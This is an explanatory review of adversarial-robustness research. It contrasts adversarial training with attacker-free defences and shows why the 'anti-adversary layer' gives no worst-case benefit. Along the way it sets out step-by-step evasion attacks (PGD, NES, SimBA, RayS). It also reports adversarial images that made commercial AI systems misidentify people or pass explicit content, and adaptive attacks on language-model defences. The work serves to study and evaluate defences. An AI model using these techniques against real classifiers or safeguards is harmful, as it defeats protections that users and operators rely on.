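# Adversarial and anti-adversarial defences: can a model be made robust without simulating an attacker?

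## What counts as a defence that uses an attacker signal?

Adversarial robustness is a machine-learning model's ability to keep giving correct or permitted outputs when someone tries to make it fail. An attacker may tamper with the model's inputs or, if the developer has published the model, with its weights, the numbers it learned in training. Researchers have worked on defences for more than a decade, and only some of these defences require the developer to attack the model first.

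An *attacker signal* is information the developer gets by searching for, or collecting, inputs or weight changes that make the model fail. A defence is *attack-simulating* if its construction uses an attacker signal, and *attacker-free* otherwise. The *base model* is the model before anyone adds the defence. Telling the two kinds of defence apart is harder than it sounds and requires some background on the attacks.

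### Adversarial examples

Most of what researchers know about attacks comes from image classifiers, models that take a picture and return a label. *Intriguing properties of neural networks* (Szegedy, Zaremba and colleagues, 2013) showed that a change a person could hardly see could make a deep neural network mislabel an image. The researchers found the change by maximising the network's prediction error, and the same change could fool a second network trained on different images. An input altered in this way is called an adversarial example. The problem is older than deep learning. *Adversarial Machine Learning* (Vassilev, Oprea and colleagues, 2025), a taxonomy from the US standards institute NIST, dates the first known instances to work by Kearns and Li in 1988, followed in 2004 by studies of how to evade spam filters.

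*Explaining and Harnessing Adversarial Examples* (Goodfellow, Shlens and Szegedy, 2014) uses simple arithmetic to explain why such a small change can have a large effect. Suppose a model multiplies each of *n* pixels by a weight and adds up the results. If every pixel shifts by a tiny amount ε, upwards where its weight is positive and downwards where it is negative, the total rises by ε × *m* × *n*, where *m* is the average size of a weight. With thousands of pixels, that increase is large. Random noise of the same size has almost no effect because the changes in different pixels cancel out.

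Goodfellow and colleagues argued that neural networks behave linearly enough for this to work on them too, and they turned the idea into a one-step attack called the fast gradient sign method. The attack uses the model's loss, a number that grows as the output departs from the right answer. The attacker computes the loss's gradient, which gives the direction of change that raises the loss fastest, and uses it to move every pixel up or down by ε, whichever raises the loss. One type of network misread about 1% of ordinary handwritten digits and 89.4% of the altered ones.

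These attacks still work. In *Laundering AI Authority with Adversarial Examples*, Zhang, Peetathawatchai and colleagues (2026) used a standard attack of this family to alter pictures against freely available image models, then showed the pictures to commercial systems, including GPT-5.4 and Claude Opus 4.6. They tried to make six such systems mistake one person for another or let through explicit images, and succeeded between 22% and 100% of the time.

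### Threat models, access and measures

A claim of robustness is meaningless without a *threat model*, a set of assumptions about the attacker. *On Evaluating Adversarial Robustness* (Carlini, Athalye and colleagues, 2019) divides these into the attacker's goals, capabilities and knowledge. The goal may be to cause any error or a particular one. For example, the maker of a malware detector worries about malicious programs that pass as harmless, but may not care about harmless programs flagged as malicious. For images, the usual limit on capability is that no pixel's value may change by more than ε. Carlini and colleagues concede that this limit matches real threats poorly, since an attacker who uses a sticker or a new camera angle has no reason to stay within it. They defend it as a precise test that a model should be able to pass before anyone trusts it with something harder.

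What an attacker knows depends mostly on their access to the model. A *white-box* attacker has the model's architecture and weights and can compute gradients. A *black-box* attacker can at most send inputs and read outputs. Some services return a probability for each possible answer, while others return only the answer. An attacker with no access to the target can still build the attack on a substitute model and hope that it transfers. Zhang and colleagues used this method to attack systems whose weights they had never seen.

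Two common measures are *robust accuracy*, the share of test inputs that the model still classifies correctly under attack, and *attack success rate*, the share of attempts, or of targets, on which the attacker gets the forbidden result. Measured robust accuracy is always an upper bound, because a better attack can only lower it. It also depends on how the tester combines attacks. If one attack breaks half the test images and another breaks the other half, robust accuracy is 50% against either attack alone but 0% against an attacker who can choose between them. Carlini and colleagues therefore want testers to count the worst result for each image. They also want testers to report *clean accuracy*, the accuracy on unaltered inputs, alongside robust accuracy, because a defence can increase robustness while making the model less accurate on those inputs.

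Language models brought three more kinds of attack. A *jailbreak* is a user's input that gets a model to produce what its developer forbids. A *prompt injection* is an instruction hidden in material the model reads, such as a web page or an email, to make the model act against its user. *Harmful fine-tuning* is further training of a released model to remove its safeguards.

### Adversarial training

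The best-known attack-simulating defence is *adversarial training*: attack the model while training it, and train it to answer correctly on whatever the attack turns up. Mądry, Makelov and colleagues (2017), in *Towards Deep Learning Models Resistant to Adversarial Attacks*, put the aim into one formula:

$$\min_{\theta}\; \mathbb{E}_{(x,y)\sim D}\Big[\max_{\delta\in S} L(\theta,\,x+\delta,\,y)\Big]$$

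Here θ stands for the weights, *x* for an image and *y* for its correct label, both drawn from the data *D*. *S* is the set of changes that the threat model allows, δ is one such change, and *L* is the loss. The inner part of the formula finds the allowed change that gives the highest loss on a given image. The outer part chooses the weights that minimise the average of this highest loss. If the resulting value were close to zero, the model would resist every change in *S*, including those that nobody had thought of trying.

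Nobody can solve the inner part exactly for a large network, so Mądry and colleagues approximate it in a loop:

1. Take a batch of training images and move each to a random starting point inside *S*.
2. Compute the gradient of the loss with respect to the image, take a small step in the direction that raises the loss, and pull the image back into *S* if it has strayed outside. Do this a fixed number of times.
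3. Adjust the weights to lower the loss on the altered images, keeping the original labels.
4. Go on to the next batch and search again, now against the adjusted weights.

The search in step 2 is *projected gradient descent*, or PGD. With α as the step size and Π as the operation that pulls the image back, each step is

$$x^{t+1}=\Pi_{x+S}\big(x^{t}+\alpha\,\mathrm{sign}(\nabla_x L(\theta,x^{t},y))\big)$$

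Step 3 needs justification, because changing the weights also changes which attack is worst. Danskin's theorem, a classical result in optimisation, shows that for smooth functions, lowering the loss at the worst point also lowers the worst-case loss. Neural networks do not quite meet its conditions, and PGD finds only an approximate worst point. Mądry and colleagues relied on experiment instead, and found that the loss under attack fell steadily during training.

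In 2017, they tested the method on CIFAR-10, a standard set of small photographs in ten classes. They trained with seven search steps per image and let each pixel move by up to 8 of its 255 brightness levels. The network classified 87.3% of ordinary images correctly, compared with 95.2% for the same architecture with ordinary training. Its accuracy was 50.0% under a seven-step attack and 45.8% under a twenty-step attack. The loss of accuracy on ordinary images, known as clean accuracy, has proved typical. In *On the Trade-Off Between Transparency and Security in Adversarial Machine Learning*, Fenaux, Srinivasa and Kerschbaum (2026) found that 66 defended CIFAR-10 models averaged 87.7% clean accuracy, against 94.0% for 12 undefended ones. The method also requires more computing, because seven search steps mean seven extra gradient calculations on every batch before the one that updates the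 weights.

Adversarial training depends heavily on the quality of the simulated attacker. When Mądry and colleagues replaced PGD with the one-step method and allowed large changes, the network learned to handle the narrow range of examples that method produces but had no resistance to PGD. *On Adaptive Attacks to Adversarial Example Defenses* (Tramèr, Carlini and colleagues, 2020) reports the same problem in several later defences that included adversarial training with a weak attack. Some of these combinations were less robust than adversarial training alone.

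### Static attacks, adaptive attacks and gradient masking

A *static attack* is one that the attacker fixed in advance, without regard to the defence under test, such as a list of jailbreak prompts copied from an earlier paper. An *adaptive attack* is one that somebody designed or optimised against the particular defence, knowing how it works. Vassilev and colleagues count adaptive attacks as white-box, while others reserve "white-box" for off-the-shelf methods that use gradients. Treating access to the model and adaptation to the defence separately is clearer, because an attacker who sees only a chatbot's replies can still tailor the next prompt to the defence. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked language-model defences this way, using an automated search that rewrote prompts based on earlier results and needed no gradients.

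Computer security ordinarily assumes that the attacker knows the design. This rule is called Kerckhoffs' principle, after a work of 1883, and it holds that a system should stay secure when everything about it is public except a key. Carlini and colleagues apply it to machine learning with two conditions on what a defender may keep secret. The secret must be easy to replace if it leaks, and an attacker must not be able to work it out by querying the system. Random numbers drawn afresh for every input meet both conditions, but a single fixed random vector added to every output fails the second, because anyone who knows what an output should have been can recover the vector by subtraction.

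Fenaux and colleagues partly disagree. They ran nine transfer attacks against 181 image models and found that attackers did better when their substitute model matched the target, defended against defended and undefended against undefended. A developer could therefore gain by not revealing whether a model has a defence. But the gain was much larger for undefended models. On CIFAR-10, a correct guess lowered their accuracy by about 49 percentage points more than a wrong one on average, compared with about 5 for defended models when the attacker used the least effective defended substitute. The setting is also narrow, since the attacker gets a single try and no queries. Secrecy also fails the first of the two conditions above, because a developer whose secret leaks would have to replace the model to get a new one.

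*Gradient masking* is the main reason a static test can mislead. A defence masks gradients when it hides the information that an attack search follows but leaves the model's errors in place. For example, a step that rounds off pixel values has a gradient of zero almost everywhere, so PGD has no direction to follow and stops, even though the harmful inputs still exist. *Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security* (Athalye, Carlini and Wagner, 2018) lists symptoms that a tester can check for: one-step attacks beat many-step ones, black-box attacks beat white-box ones, or an attacker with no limit on the size of the change still fails on some images. The last is a clear sign of masking, because an attacker who may change everything can always succeed. Testers can get around masking by taking directions from another source, such as a substitute model or a smooth approximation of the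 step that hides the gradient. Attacker-free defences can mask gradients, and so can adversarial training against a weak attack, when the model learns to make its gradients point in useless directions.

### Four levels of attacker information

Defences differ in how much information about attackers goes into building them, which is a useful way to sort them. Only information used in the construction counts. Every designer has read about attacks, so if general knowledge counted, no defence would be attacker-free.

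*No attacker information.* Prompt Sandwiching, a defence against prompt injection, repeats the user's request after the untrusted text so that the model keeps following it. Setting it up requires no example of an injection or description of what one might look like.

*The set of permitted changes.* Here the developer knows which changes the attacker may make but never searches for one that fools the model. The simplest example is training on images with random noise of the permitted size. Goodfellow and colleagues tried two versions of this as a control for adversarial training on handwritten digits. The networks trained with noise still misread 86.2% and 90.4% of adversarial examples, hardly different from the 89.4% with no defence. Adversarial training reduced this to 17.9%. The noise and the attack came from the same set of changes, so the comparison isolates what search adds. The 17.9%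 is less reliable, because the test used the same one-step attack as the training. Noise can do better when the developer also uses it at run time, as in randomised smoothing, which classifies many noisy copies of each input and takes a vote.

Some developers gather or generate a stored collection of attacks and train on it as on any other data. StruQ, another defence against prompt injection, does this. Nasr and colleagues class it as training against existing attacks, with examples from a mixture of hand-made rules and optimisation. The collection does not change as the model learns, so the procedure does not search for the weaknesses that remain after training.

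*A live search against the current model.* This is adversarial training as Mądry and colleagues practise it, with new attacks for every batch.

The first two levels are attacker-free and the last two are attack-simulating. The order helps keep comparisons clear but doesn't rank defences by strength. One-step adversarial training is at the top level and can still fail completely against PGD. Some methods also don't fit a single level. Cascade adversarial training, which Athalye and colleagues examined, uses both a stored collection and a live search, because the developer attacks a first model with a many-step search, stores the results, and trains a second model on them together with fresh one-step attacks.

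Two further cases cause more trouble in practice. An attacker-free defence may be added to a base model that is not attacker-free. The robust accuracy of the pair then doesn't show how much each part contributed, unless the tester also reports the base model's robust accuracy alone. A developer may also build a defence without attacks, but then try a dozen settings against a test attack and keep the best. The test attack has then shaped the defence, although the defence's description may never mention it.

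"Anti-adversarial" in its wide sense refers loosely to any attacker-free method. The narrow sense comes from *Combating Adversaries with Anti-Adversaries* (Alfarra, Pérez and colleagues, 2021). Its *anti-adversary layer* is an attacker-free defence that shifts each input in the direction that raises the model's confidence in its own first prediction. In writing on AI alignment, "anti-adversarial training" has also meant something unrelated: training a model on situations in which it could do something exceptionally good, such as exposing another AI's dangerous plan, so that it takes the chance when one comes.

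## How does the anti-adversary layer work, and why does it fail against an adaptive attacker?

An attacker lowers a classifier's confidence in the right answer until it gives a wrong one. The anti-adversary layer of Alfarra and colleagues sits in front of a trained classifier and is meant to raise that confidence again. But the layer has no access to the right answer, so it strengthens whichever answer the classifier gives first, whether right or wrong.

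### The algorithm

Let *f* be the base model, *x* an image and *L* the cross-entropy loss, which is small when the model gives a high probability to a chosen label. The layer has two settings, a number of steps *K* and a step size α. For every image it does the following:

1. Run *f* on *x* and note the label with the highest score, written ŷ.
2. Start with a shift γ of zero.
3. Compute the gradient of the loss on ŷ at the shifted image, and move every pixel by α in whichever direction lowers that loss. Do this *K* times.
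4. Run *f* on *x* + γ and return the result.

Step 3 in symbols is

$$\gamma^{k+1}=\gamma^{k}-\alpha\,\mathrm{sign}\big(\nabla_{\gamma} L(f(x+\gamma^{k}),\hat{y})\big)$$

This is nearly the PGD attack, but it has a minus sign where PGD has a plus, uses the predicted label ŷ instead of the true label *y*, and has no step that pulls the image back if it moves too far. In most of their tests, Alfarra and colleagues used two steps of 0.15 on a scale where a pixel runs from 0 to 1. Each step is about 38 of the 255 brightness levels, so the two together can shift a pixel by up to 76 levels. The attackers in the same tests could change a pixel by only 8.

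The layer needs no training, but it adds computation at run time. Each image takes *K* + 1 ordinary runs of the model and *K* gradient calculations, compared with a single run for the undefended model. Alfarra and colleagues call the added computation marginal when *K* is small.

### Results against attacks fixed in advance

Some of the most striking results concern query attacks, in which the attacker can only send images and read the scores that come back. *Black-box Adversarial Attacks with Limited Queries and Information* (Ilyas, Engstrom and colleagues, 2018) introduced one such attack, NES (natural evolution strategies). It estimates the gradient, which the attacker cannot see, entirely from differences between scores. The attacker adds a random noise pattern to the image, subtracts the same pattern from the original image, and gets the model's score for each version. The difference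 between the two scores shows how far the pattern points towards or away from the label in question. Averaging over many patterns gives an approximate gradient, which the attacker uses to take PGD steps.

Alfarra and colleagues ran NES with 10,000 queries per image on an ordinary CIFAR-10 network, using 1,000 test images and a small step size of 0.01. The network's accuracy under attack was 4.8% without the layer and 72.7% with it, while its clean accuracy stayed at 93.7%. On ImageNet, a much larger collection of photographs, the layer raised accuracy under the same attack from 21.0% to 66.0%. SND, a rival defence that adds a little random noise to each input, reached only 25.5% on CIFAR-10.

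They also tested the layer on adversarially trained models, using AutoAttack from *Reliable Evaluation of Adversarial Robustness with an Ensemble of Diverse Parameter-free Attacks* (Croce and Hein, 2020). AutoAttack runs four attacks and counts the model as failing on an image if any of them succeeds. Three of the attacks, FAB and two versions of PGD that adjust their own step size, use gradients. The fourth, Square Attack, needs only the model's output scores. It changes small, random squares of pixels in the image and keeps the changes that help the attack.

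The strongest base model in these tests was trained with adversarial weight perturbation (AWP), a form of adversarial training. When Alfarra and colleagues added the layer, the model's accuracy under AutoAttack rose from 60.53% to 79.21%, and its clean accuracy stayed at 88.25%. Four other adversarially trained CIFAR-10 models gained between 18.6 and 20.7 percentage points. Two models for CIFAR-100, a similar dataset with 100 classes, gained 10 to 12. Because AWP itself simulates attacks, only the additional 18.7 points could be credited to the layer.

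AutoAttack is a static attack here because none of its four parts accounts for a layer that shifts the input, although two of them adapt their step size to the progress of the search. Croce and Hein proposed AutoAttack as a minimum test for new defences and denied that it was the ultimate attack.

The detailed results also show a symptom of gradient masking, which is that a black-box attack beats white-box attacks. On MART, an adversarially trained model, the best gradient attack left 56.8% accuracy without the layer, and the black-box Square Attack left 64.9%. This is the normal order, since an attacker who can compute gradients has more information. With the layer, the order reversed, as the best gradient attack left 80.5% and Square Attack left 78.0%. The same happened on another model, HYDRA. Athalye and colleagues had listed this symptom four years before the layer was published at a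 conference.

The query attacks on the ordinary network gave a weaker hint of the same kind. Under Bandits, a relative of NES, the defended network had 85.5% accuracy after 5,000 queries and 86.4% after 10,000. The difference is only nine images, but an attack that was making progress would have lowered the accuracy further with twice the queries.

### What the theorem assumes and shows

Alfarra and colleagues back these results with a theorem about SimBA, a simple score-based attack introduced in *Simple Black-box Adversarial Attacks* (Guo, Gardner and colleagues, 2019). The attacker picks a random direction, such as one colour of one pixel, and adds a small step in that direction. If the model's score for the right label falls, the attacker keeps the step. Otherwise the attacker tries subtracting the step, and if that doesn't lower the score either, moves on to another direction.

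The theorem compares how many queries SimBA needs with and without the layer. It makes these assumptions:

- The attacker may change the image without limit, tries both signs of every step, and can draw the same direction more than once.
- The loss is smooth, meaning that its gradient changes no faster than some constant *M* allows, and the attacker's step ε is small compared with 1/*M*.
- The layer takes a single step, along the same direction that SimBA has just drawn, with size (1 − *c*)ε for some *c* below 1.
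- The loss is locally monotone: if a small step one way raises it, a small step the other way lowers it. This condition appears only in the version of the theorem in the paper's appendix.

The conclusion has two parts. If the layer's step is at least as large as the attacker's (*c* ≤ 0), SimBA never succeeds. If the layer's step is smaller, the number of queries grows by the factor

$$G(c)=\frac{\rho/n-M\varepsilon/2}{c\,(\rho/n-M\varepsilon c/2)}$$

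where *n* is the number of pixel values and ρ is a threshold for the size of the gradient. For very small attack steps this is close to 1/*c*, so a layer that moves half as far as the attacker would double the attacker's bill.

These assumptions describe a different defence from the one in the experiments. A real layer receives only the image, not the direction the attacker has just tried, and it moves all the pixels at once by the sign of a gradient. The theorem also gives a number of queries that is enough to bring the expected gradient below ρ, whereas a defender wants to know how many queries it takes to change the label. Showing that a larger budget is enough with the layer does not show that a smaller one would fail. The proof also contains a more basic mistake, which is easiest to see in an example.

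### Same decisions, different scores

Write *g* for the base model with the layer in front. For an image *x* with true label *y*, the successful attacks on *f* are the permitted changes δ that make *f* give *x* + δ a label other than *y*:

$$A_f(x)=\{\delta\in S:\ \text{label of } f(x+\delta)\neq y\}$$

The layer receives *x* + δ, takes the label *f* assigns to it, and raises the model's confidence in that label. If this never changes the label, *f* and *g* assign the same label to every input. The same attacks therefore succeed against both, and both have the same accuracy under the best possible attack.

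Alfarra and colleagues use half of this argument themselves to explain why the layer doesn't reduce clean accuracy. They point out that *g* must classify correctly every image that *f* classifies correctly, because the layer only raises confidence in the top prediction. But the same reasoning implies that *g* also misclassifies every image that *f* misclassifies, including every successful attack.

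The argument has a small gap, because higher confidence in the chosen label does not always preserve it when there are more than two classes. With ten, the chosen label could rise from 30% to 35% while another jumps to 40%. A large step can also overshoot the region where the label holds, because a signed step moves each pixel by the full α however weak the gradient is. *Evaluating the Adversarial Robustness of Adaptive Test-time Defenses* (Croce, Gowal and colleagues, 2022) found that changes of label were rare and disappeared with a smaller step. Clean accuracy also suggests that they are rare. With two steps of 0.15, it moved by less than a tenth of a point on the five CIFAR-10 models, and by at most one point on CIFAR-100.

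A model whose input is a single number, *x*, can show what the layer changes. Suppose the model's confidence in "positive" is σ(4*x*), where σ(*z*) = 1/(1 + e^(−*z*)) is the logistic function, which maps any number *z* to a value between 0 and 1. The boundary between "positive" and "negative" is then at *x* = 0. Suppose also that the layer moves each input 0.4 further from the boundary, and that a clean input of 0.3 has the true label "positive".

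| Input | Confidence in "positive", base model | Where the layer moves it | Confidence in "positive", with layer | Label from both |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.30 (clean) | 0.769 | 0.70 | 0.943 | positive |
| 0.25 (one attack step of 0.05) | 0.731 | 0.65 | 0.931 | positive |
| −0.10 (attack complete) | 0.401 | −0.50 | 0.119 | negative |

The completed attack works on both models. The defended model gives the wrong answer, "negative", with 88% confidence, compared with 60% for the base model. The attacker had to move the input by 0.3 in both cases, because they control the input and the boundary for that input is still at 0.

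The defended model gives the attacker different information on the way to the boundary. The first step of 0.05 lowers the base model's score by 0.037 but the defended model's by only 0.012, because the curve is flatter further from the boundary and the layer always takes the score from a point further out. The defended model's confidence in "positive" is still above 0.83 close to the boundary, and it drops below 0.17 just past it. An attacker who relies on scores therefore sees them fall slowly, with little sign of how near the boundary is.

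In this example the slope is still easy to read, but it becomes harder to read when the model is more confident. If the confidence is σ(40*x*), the step from 0.30 to 0.25 changes the base model's score by about 0.00004, which a computer can record. With the layer, both scores differ from 1 by less than a hundred-billionth. Ordinary 32-bit arithmetic rounds both to exactly 1, so the attacker sees no change. Croce and Hein had already shown the same effect without the layer. They took a published CIFAR-10 model whose scores were so extreme that nearly all of its gradients came out as zero, so PGD had no gradient to follow. Dividing the scores by a constant restored the gradients without changing any of the model's decisions, and the measured robust accuracy was much lower.

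Gradient attacks have another problem. The layer's shift depends only on the signs of gradients, and a sign stays constant until it flips, so its derivative is zero almost everywhere. An attack that differentiates through the whole system therefore gets the gradient of *f* at the shifted image, up to 76 brightness levels away per pixel, when it needs the direction from the image it is changing. This probably explains why AWP kept 81.5% accuracy under one of AutoAttack's gradient attacks with the layer, compared with 60.5% without it. Croce and Hein had designed that attack's loss to be immune to rescaled scores, but the layer does more than multiply the scores by a constant.

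The one-number model is also a counterexample to the theorem. Its loss is smooth and monotone, and the layer's step of 0.4 is eight times the attacker's 0.05, so the theorem implies that SimBA can never succeed. But each step towards the boundary lowers the score, from 0.943 to 0.931, then 0.917, 0.900 and so on. SimBA keeps these steps, and the seventh takes the input to −0.05, where both models get it wrong. The error in the proof is that it adds the layer's shift to the attacker's image at each round. The layer actually shifts a temporary copy inside the model and leaves the attacker's image unchanged. The appendix's version for white-box attackers has the same flaw.

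### An attack that reads only labels

If the layer changes scores but not decisions, it should not affect an attack that uses only the predicted labels. Such attacks used to need far more queries than attacks that use scores. When Ilyas and colleagues tried to get ImageNet pictures classified as a particular wrong class, they needed a median of 11,550 queries per picture with scores and 2.7 million with only labels.

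RayS, from Chen and Gu (2020), in *RayS*, made label-only attacks much cheaper. It measures how far an image is from a change of label along a given direction, and looks for the direction in which that distance is shortest. It considers only directions in which every pixel value moves by the same amount, up or down. The attack starts with all of them moving up and works as follows:

1. Reverse the direction for one block of the image.
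2. Ask the model for the label at the best distance found so far, along this new direction. If the label is still the right one, the new direction is no better, and the attack drops it after a single query.
3. If the label is wrong, find the new, shorter distance by repeatedly halving the interval.
4. Go through all the blocks, then cut the image into smaller blocks and continue.

The attack succeeds if the shortest distance is within the permitted change. On an ordinary ImageNet network, RayS succeeded for 99.8% of images with a median of 296 queries. Its task was easier than that of Ilyas and colleagues because any wrong label counted as a success.

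RayS is deterministic, so if two models give the same label to every input, it sends them the same queries in the same order and ends with the same accuracy. Croce and colleagues ran it with 10,000 queries on the AWP model, using the layer's original code and settings. Alfarra and colleagues had reported 79.2% for the defended model, but it kept 66.6%, the same as the base model alone.

They then tried the most obvious adaptive attack, which is to run a gradient attack on the base model and submit the resulting images to the defended one. Both models kept 63.7% accuracy. The table compares these tests with the original ones on the AWP model. The first three rows come from Alfarra and colleagues and the last two from Croce and colleagues.

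| Attack | What the attacker uses | Accuracy, base model | Accuracy, with layer |
|---|---|---|---|
| NES | scores | 80.1% | 86.9% |
| Square Attack | scores | 66.2% | 80.7% |
| AutoAttack | gradients and scores | 60.5% | 79.2% |
| RayS | labels | 66.6% | 66.6% |
| PGD variant run on the base model | gradients of the base model | 63.7% | 63.7% |

The base AWP model has 66.6% accuracy under RayS and 60.5% under AutoAttack. The two papers' results are consistent, because RayS uses only the model's predicted labels and so works with less information than AutoAttack. Chen and Gu found the same pattern in two other adversarially trained models, where RayS left 54.0% and 57.3% accuracy and gradient attacks left 50.6% and 55.3%. Each figure is an upper bound on robust accuracy, so the lowest one for the AWP model, 60.5%, is closest to the true value.

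The images with which AutoAttack beat the base model will also beat the model with the layer, except in the rare cases where the layer overshoots. The reported 79.2% should therefore be about 60.5%, which leaves none of the 18.7-point gain. Croce and colleagues did not repeat the test on the ordinary network that seemed to go from 4.8% to 72.7% under NES, but the argument does not depend on how the base model was trained, so an ordinary network with the layer should be about as easy to beat as one without it.

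*Interpretability-Guided Test-Time Adversarial Defense* (Kulkarni and Weng, 2024) later tested the layer on three other adversarially trained models. It counted an image as lost if any of nine attacks succeeded, three of them aimed at the defended model and six run on the base model. Robust accuracy was 51.01%, 52.45% and 56.12% for the base models, and 51.00%, 52.45% and 56.11% with the layer added. These are differences of at most one image in a test set of 10,000. The paper was presenting a competing defence, but its results match what the argument about decisions predicts for any base model.

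Croce and colleagues tested nine defences, including the anti-adversary layer, and measured the layer's inference time at eight times that of the base model. With two steps, the layer needs three ordinary runs and two gradient calculations, each of which takes about as long as two runs. The original code also made one unnecessary run. Kulkarni and Weng rank the layer as the strongest of the nine because it at least did not make its base model worse.

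Alfarra and colleagues had tried label-only attacks themselves, using two older methods on 100 images. Under one attack, accuracy was 86% with and without the layer. Under the other, it was 86% with the layer and 85% without it. They described this as a notable improvement, though the difference is a single image. Both attacks had little effect, since the model's clean accuracy on those images was 88%. Croce and colleagues suspected that Alfarra and colleagues had used the attacks incorrectly or run too few iterations. Tests by Chen and Gu suggest that the choice of attack could matter too. On one adversarially trained model with 87.4% clean accuracy, two older label-only attacks reduced accuracy to 85.1% and 76.8%, while RayS reduced it to 54.0%.

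RayS also found weaknesses in defences that did search for attacks during training. One variant of adversarial training appeared to keep 75.3% accuracy under a 100-step PGD attack but kept only 46.9% under RayS.

### The base model as a lower bound and an upper bound

Alfarra and colleagues discuss adaptive attacks briefly, without reporting a measured accuracy. They note that the layer relies on the base model's first label, so an attacker who knows about the layer can look for a change that makes the base model choose a wrong label, which the layer will then reinforce. They conclude that whatever fools the base model *f* also fools the defended model *g*. From this they infer that the base model's robust accuracy is a lower bound on the defended model's, so adding the layer can only help.

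The inference is backwards, because if every successful attack on *f* also succeeds against *g*, then the robust accuracy of *g* can be at most that of *f*. This gives an upper bound. A lower bound needs the converse, that every successful attack on *g* also succeeds against *f*.

The converse is also true, again except when the layer overshoots, because the two models give the same labels. So the base model's robust accuracy is both a lower and an upper bound on the robust accuracy with the layer added, and the layer's worst-case benefit is zero. Overshooting can move the result slightly in either direction. It may accidentally correct the label of an attacked image, or cause an error on one that the base model would have got right, as it seems to have done for one image in two of the three tests by Kulkarni and Weng. Elsewhere in their paper, Alfarra and colleagues say that the layer improves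 worst-case robustness under adaptive attacks, which their own argument rules out.

They also call the adaptive attacker the least realistic one, since it must know how the defence works, and so they give worst-case tests little weight in practice. But RayS needs only the labels that the service returns. An attacker can use it without knowing the layer exists, and do exactly as well as if the layer were not there.

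## What is the case for deploying a defence that has never seen an attack?

The failure of one layer doesn't settle whether attacker-free defences are a good idea. Their supporters make six claims: these defences are easy to add to a finished model; worst-case tests overstate what real attackers can do; training on simulated attacks leaves a model open to other attacks; building simulated attackers is itself hazardous; adversarially trained models help people attack other models; and training against attacks makes a model less accurate or less helpful.

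### Adding a defence to a finished model

Adversarial training changes a model's weights, so a developer who has already trained a model must train it again. Adding a layer in front of the model avoids this, which helps anyone who lacks the resources to retrain the model they use. Alfarra and colleagues present their layer as a way to avoid the heavy training computation and lost accuracy of the few defences that have withstood scrutiny.

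Some attacker-free defences do reduce accuracy on clean inputs. When Alfarra and colleagues added the random-noise defence SND to the adversarially trained AWP model, clean accuracy fell from 88.25% to 70.03%, and accuracy under AutoAttack fell from 60.53% to 27.04%. Croce and colleagues found that four of the nine defences they tested weakened a base model that was already robust, while the others improved it slightly but required much more computation.

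That extra computation happens at run time. According to *Robust Feature Inference* (2023), defences that adjust the input or the model for each query at least double the computation needed for inference, and one multiplies it by 500. Adversarial training needs more computation at the start but adds none to later queries, so which approach uses less overall depends on how many queries the model receives. On CIFAR-10, seven-step adversarial training adds seven gradient calculations per image, each equivalent to about three ordinary runs of the model. Over 100 passes through the 50,000 training images, this adds roughly 105 million runs. The two-step anti-adversary layer adds the equivalent of six runs to every query, so it uses more additional computation than adversarial training after about 17.5 million queries. A popular online service would reach that number, though a small internal tool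 may never do so.

### What real attackers can see

Alfarra and colleagues argue that black-box attacks are the realistic case, because commercial services reveal little beyond a model's predictions. When two classifiers do equally well in worst-case tests, they say a developer should prefer the one that does better against black-box attackers, who are weaker but more common. Their layer looks worth adding by that standard, but it has no effect on RayS, which a black-box attacker can choose to use.

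Some evidence suggests that real attackers don't use gradients. *A No-Defense Defense Against Gradient-Based Adversarial Attacks on ML-NIDS* (2026) concerns network intrusion detection, where a model checks network traffic for signs of an attack. Outsiders can't see the model's gradients, and these systems aren't designed to answer their queries. The model's input measurements also depend on one another, so an attacker can't change them freely. The paper cites Apruzzese and colleagues, who found no concrete evidence of anyone using gradients to evade an intrusion detector in the real world. The paper describes blind changes to the traffic, which need neither queries nor knowledge of the model, as the most practical attack.

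This evidence counts against attackers using gradients, but they could still adapt to a defence without them. *Evaluating the Robustness of a Production Malware Detection System* (2025) tests an attack called greedy coordinate gradient (GCG), which uses gradients to pick promising changes to a file, tries many of them and keeps the best. The paper explains that an attacker without gradients can pick the changes at random and still keep the best. This takes more trials, but *AutoAdvExBench* (2025), a benchmark of how well AI systems can break published defences, notes that gradient-free search alone is often enough to break a defence.

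The same question came up in a dispute over Sabre, an image defence whose designers said gradient-free attacks were outside its scope. *Cutting through buggy adversarial example defenses* (2024) replies that anyone who can compute gradients can also attack without them, so a defence against white-box attackers must also withstand black-box methods. It adds that hundreds of published defences already resist some fixed set of attacks, and that people will try to break any defence that is published.

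An attacker's limited access to the model is also a poor reason to prefer an attacker-free defence to adversarial training. Djilani, Ghamizi and Cordy (2024), in *RobustBlack*, ran 13 black-box attacks against defended ImageNet models. LGV, one of the strongest attacks that transfer from a substitute model, succeeded 87.39% of the time against an undefended model but only 2.17% of the time against one trained with a simple adversarial method from 2020. Models hardened against AutoAttack, which is mostly white-box, also resisted black-box attacks better. By contrast, the paper cites a finding that preprocessing the input made black-box attacks seven times less effective when the attacker didn't know about it, but that attacks that took it into account overcame it easily.

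A service can also limit how many queries each user sends. Fenaux and colleagues expect such limits to stop most query attacks, so they studied transfer attacks instead. The limit would have to be strict, because RayS can succeed with a few hundred queries. The service would also have to stop attackers from spreading queries over many accounts.

### Whether a company needs a robust model at all

Raff, Benaroch and Farris (2025), in *You Don’t Need Robust Machine Learning to Manage Adversarial Attack Risks*, go further and argue that most companies have no immediate need for a robust model. They compare the expected cost of errors with an ordinary model, on the left, and a robust one, on the right:

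$$c_n(1-p)(1-A)+c_a\,p \;=\; c_n(1-p)(1-A+z)+c_a\,p\,(1-A+z)$$

Here *A* is the ordinary model's accuracy, *z* is how far the robust model's accuracy falls below that, and *p* is the share of inputs that are attacks. The loss from an ordinary error is *c*ₙ, and the loss from a successful attack is *c*ₐ. The equation assumes that every attack on the ordinary model succeeds and that the robust model errs no more often on attacks than on other inputs.

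If both kinds of error are equally harmful, the two sides are equal when *z* = *pA*. If a model has 95% accuracy and 1% of its inputs are attacks, the robust version can lose at most 0.95 percentage points of accuracy before it becomes the worse choice. Existing defences usually lose more than that. The models that Fenaux and colleagues collected averaged 75.8% accuracy on ImageNet without a defence and 71.7% with one, and the gap on CIFAR-10 was larger. The computing needed for training also counts against the robust model. Raff and colleagues estimate that robust training can easily take 100 to 1,000 times as much computing as ordinary training, far above the roughly eightfold increase per batch for the seven-step method on CIFAR-10.

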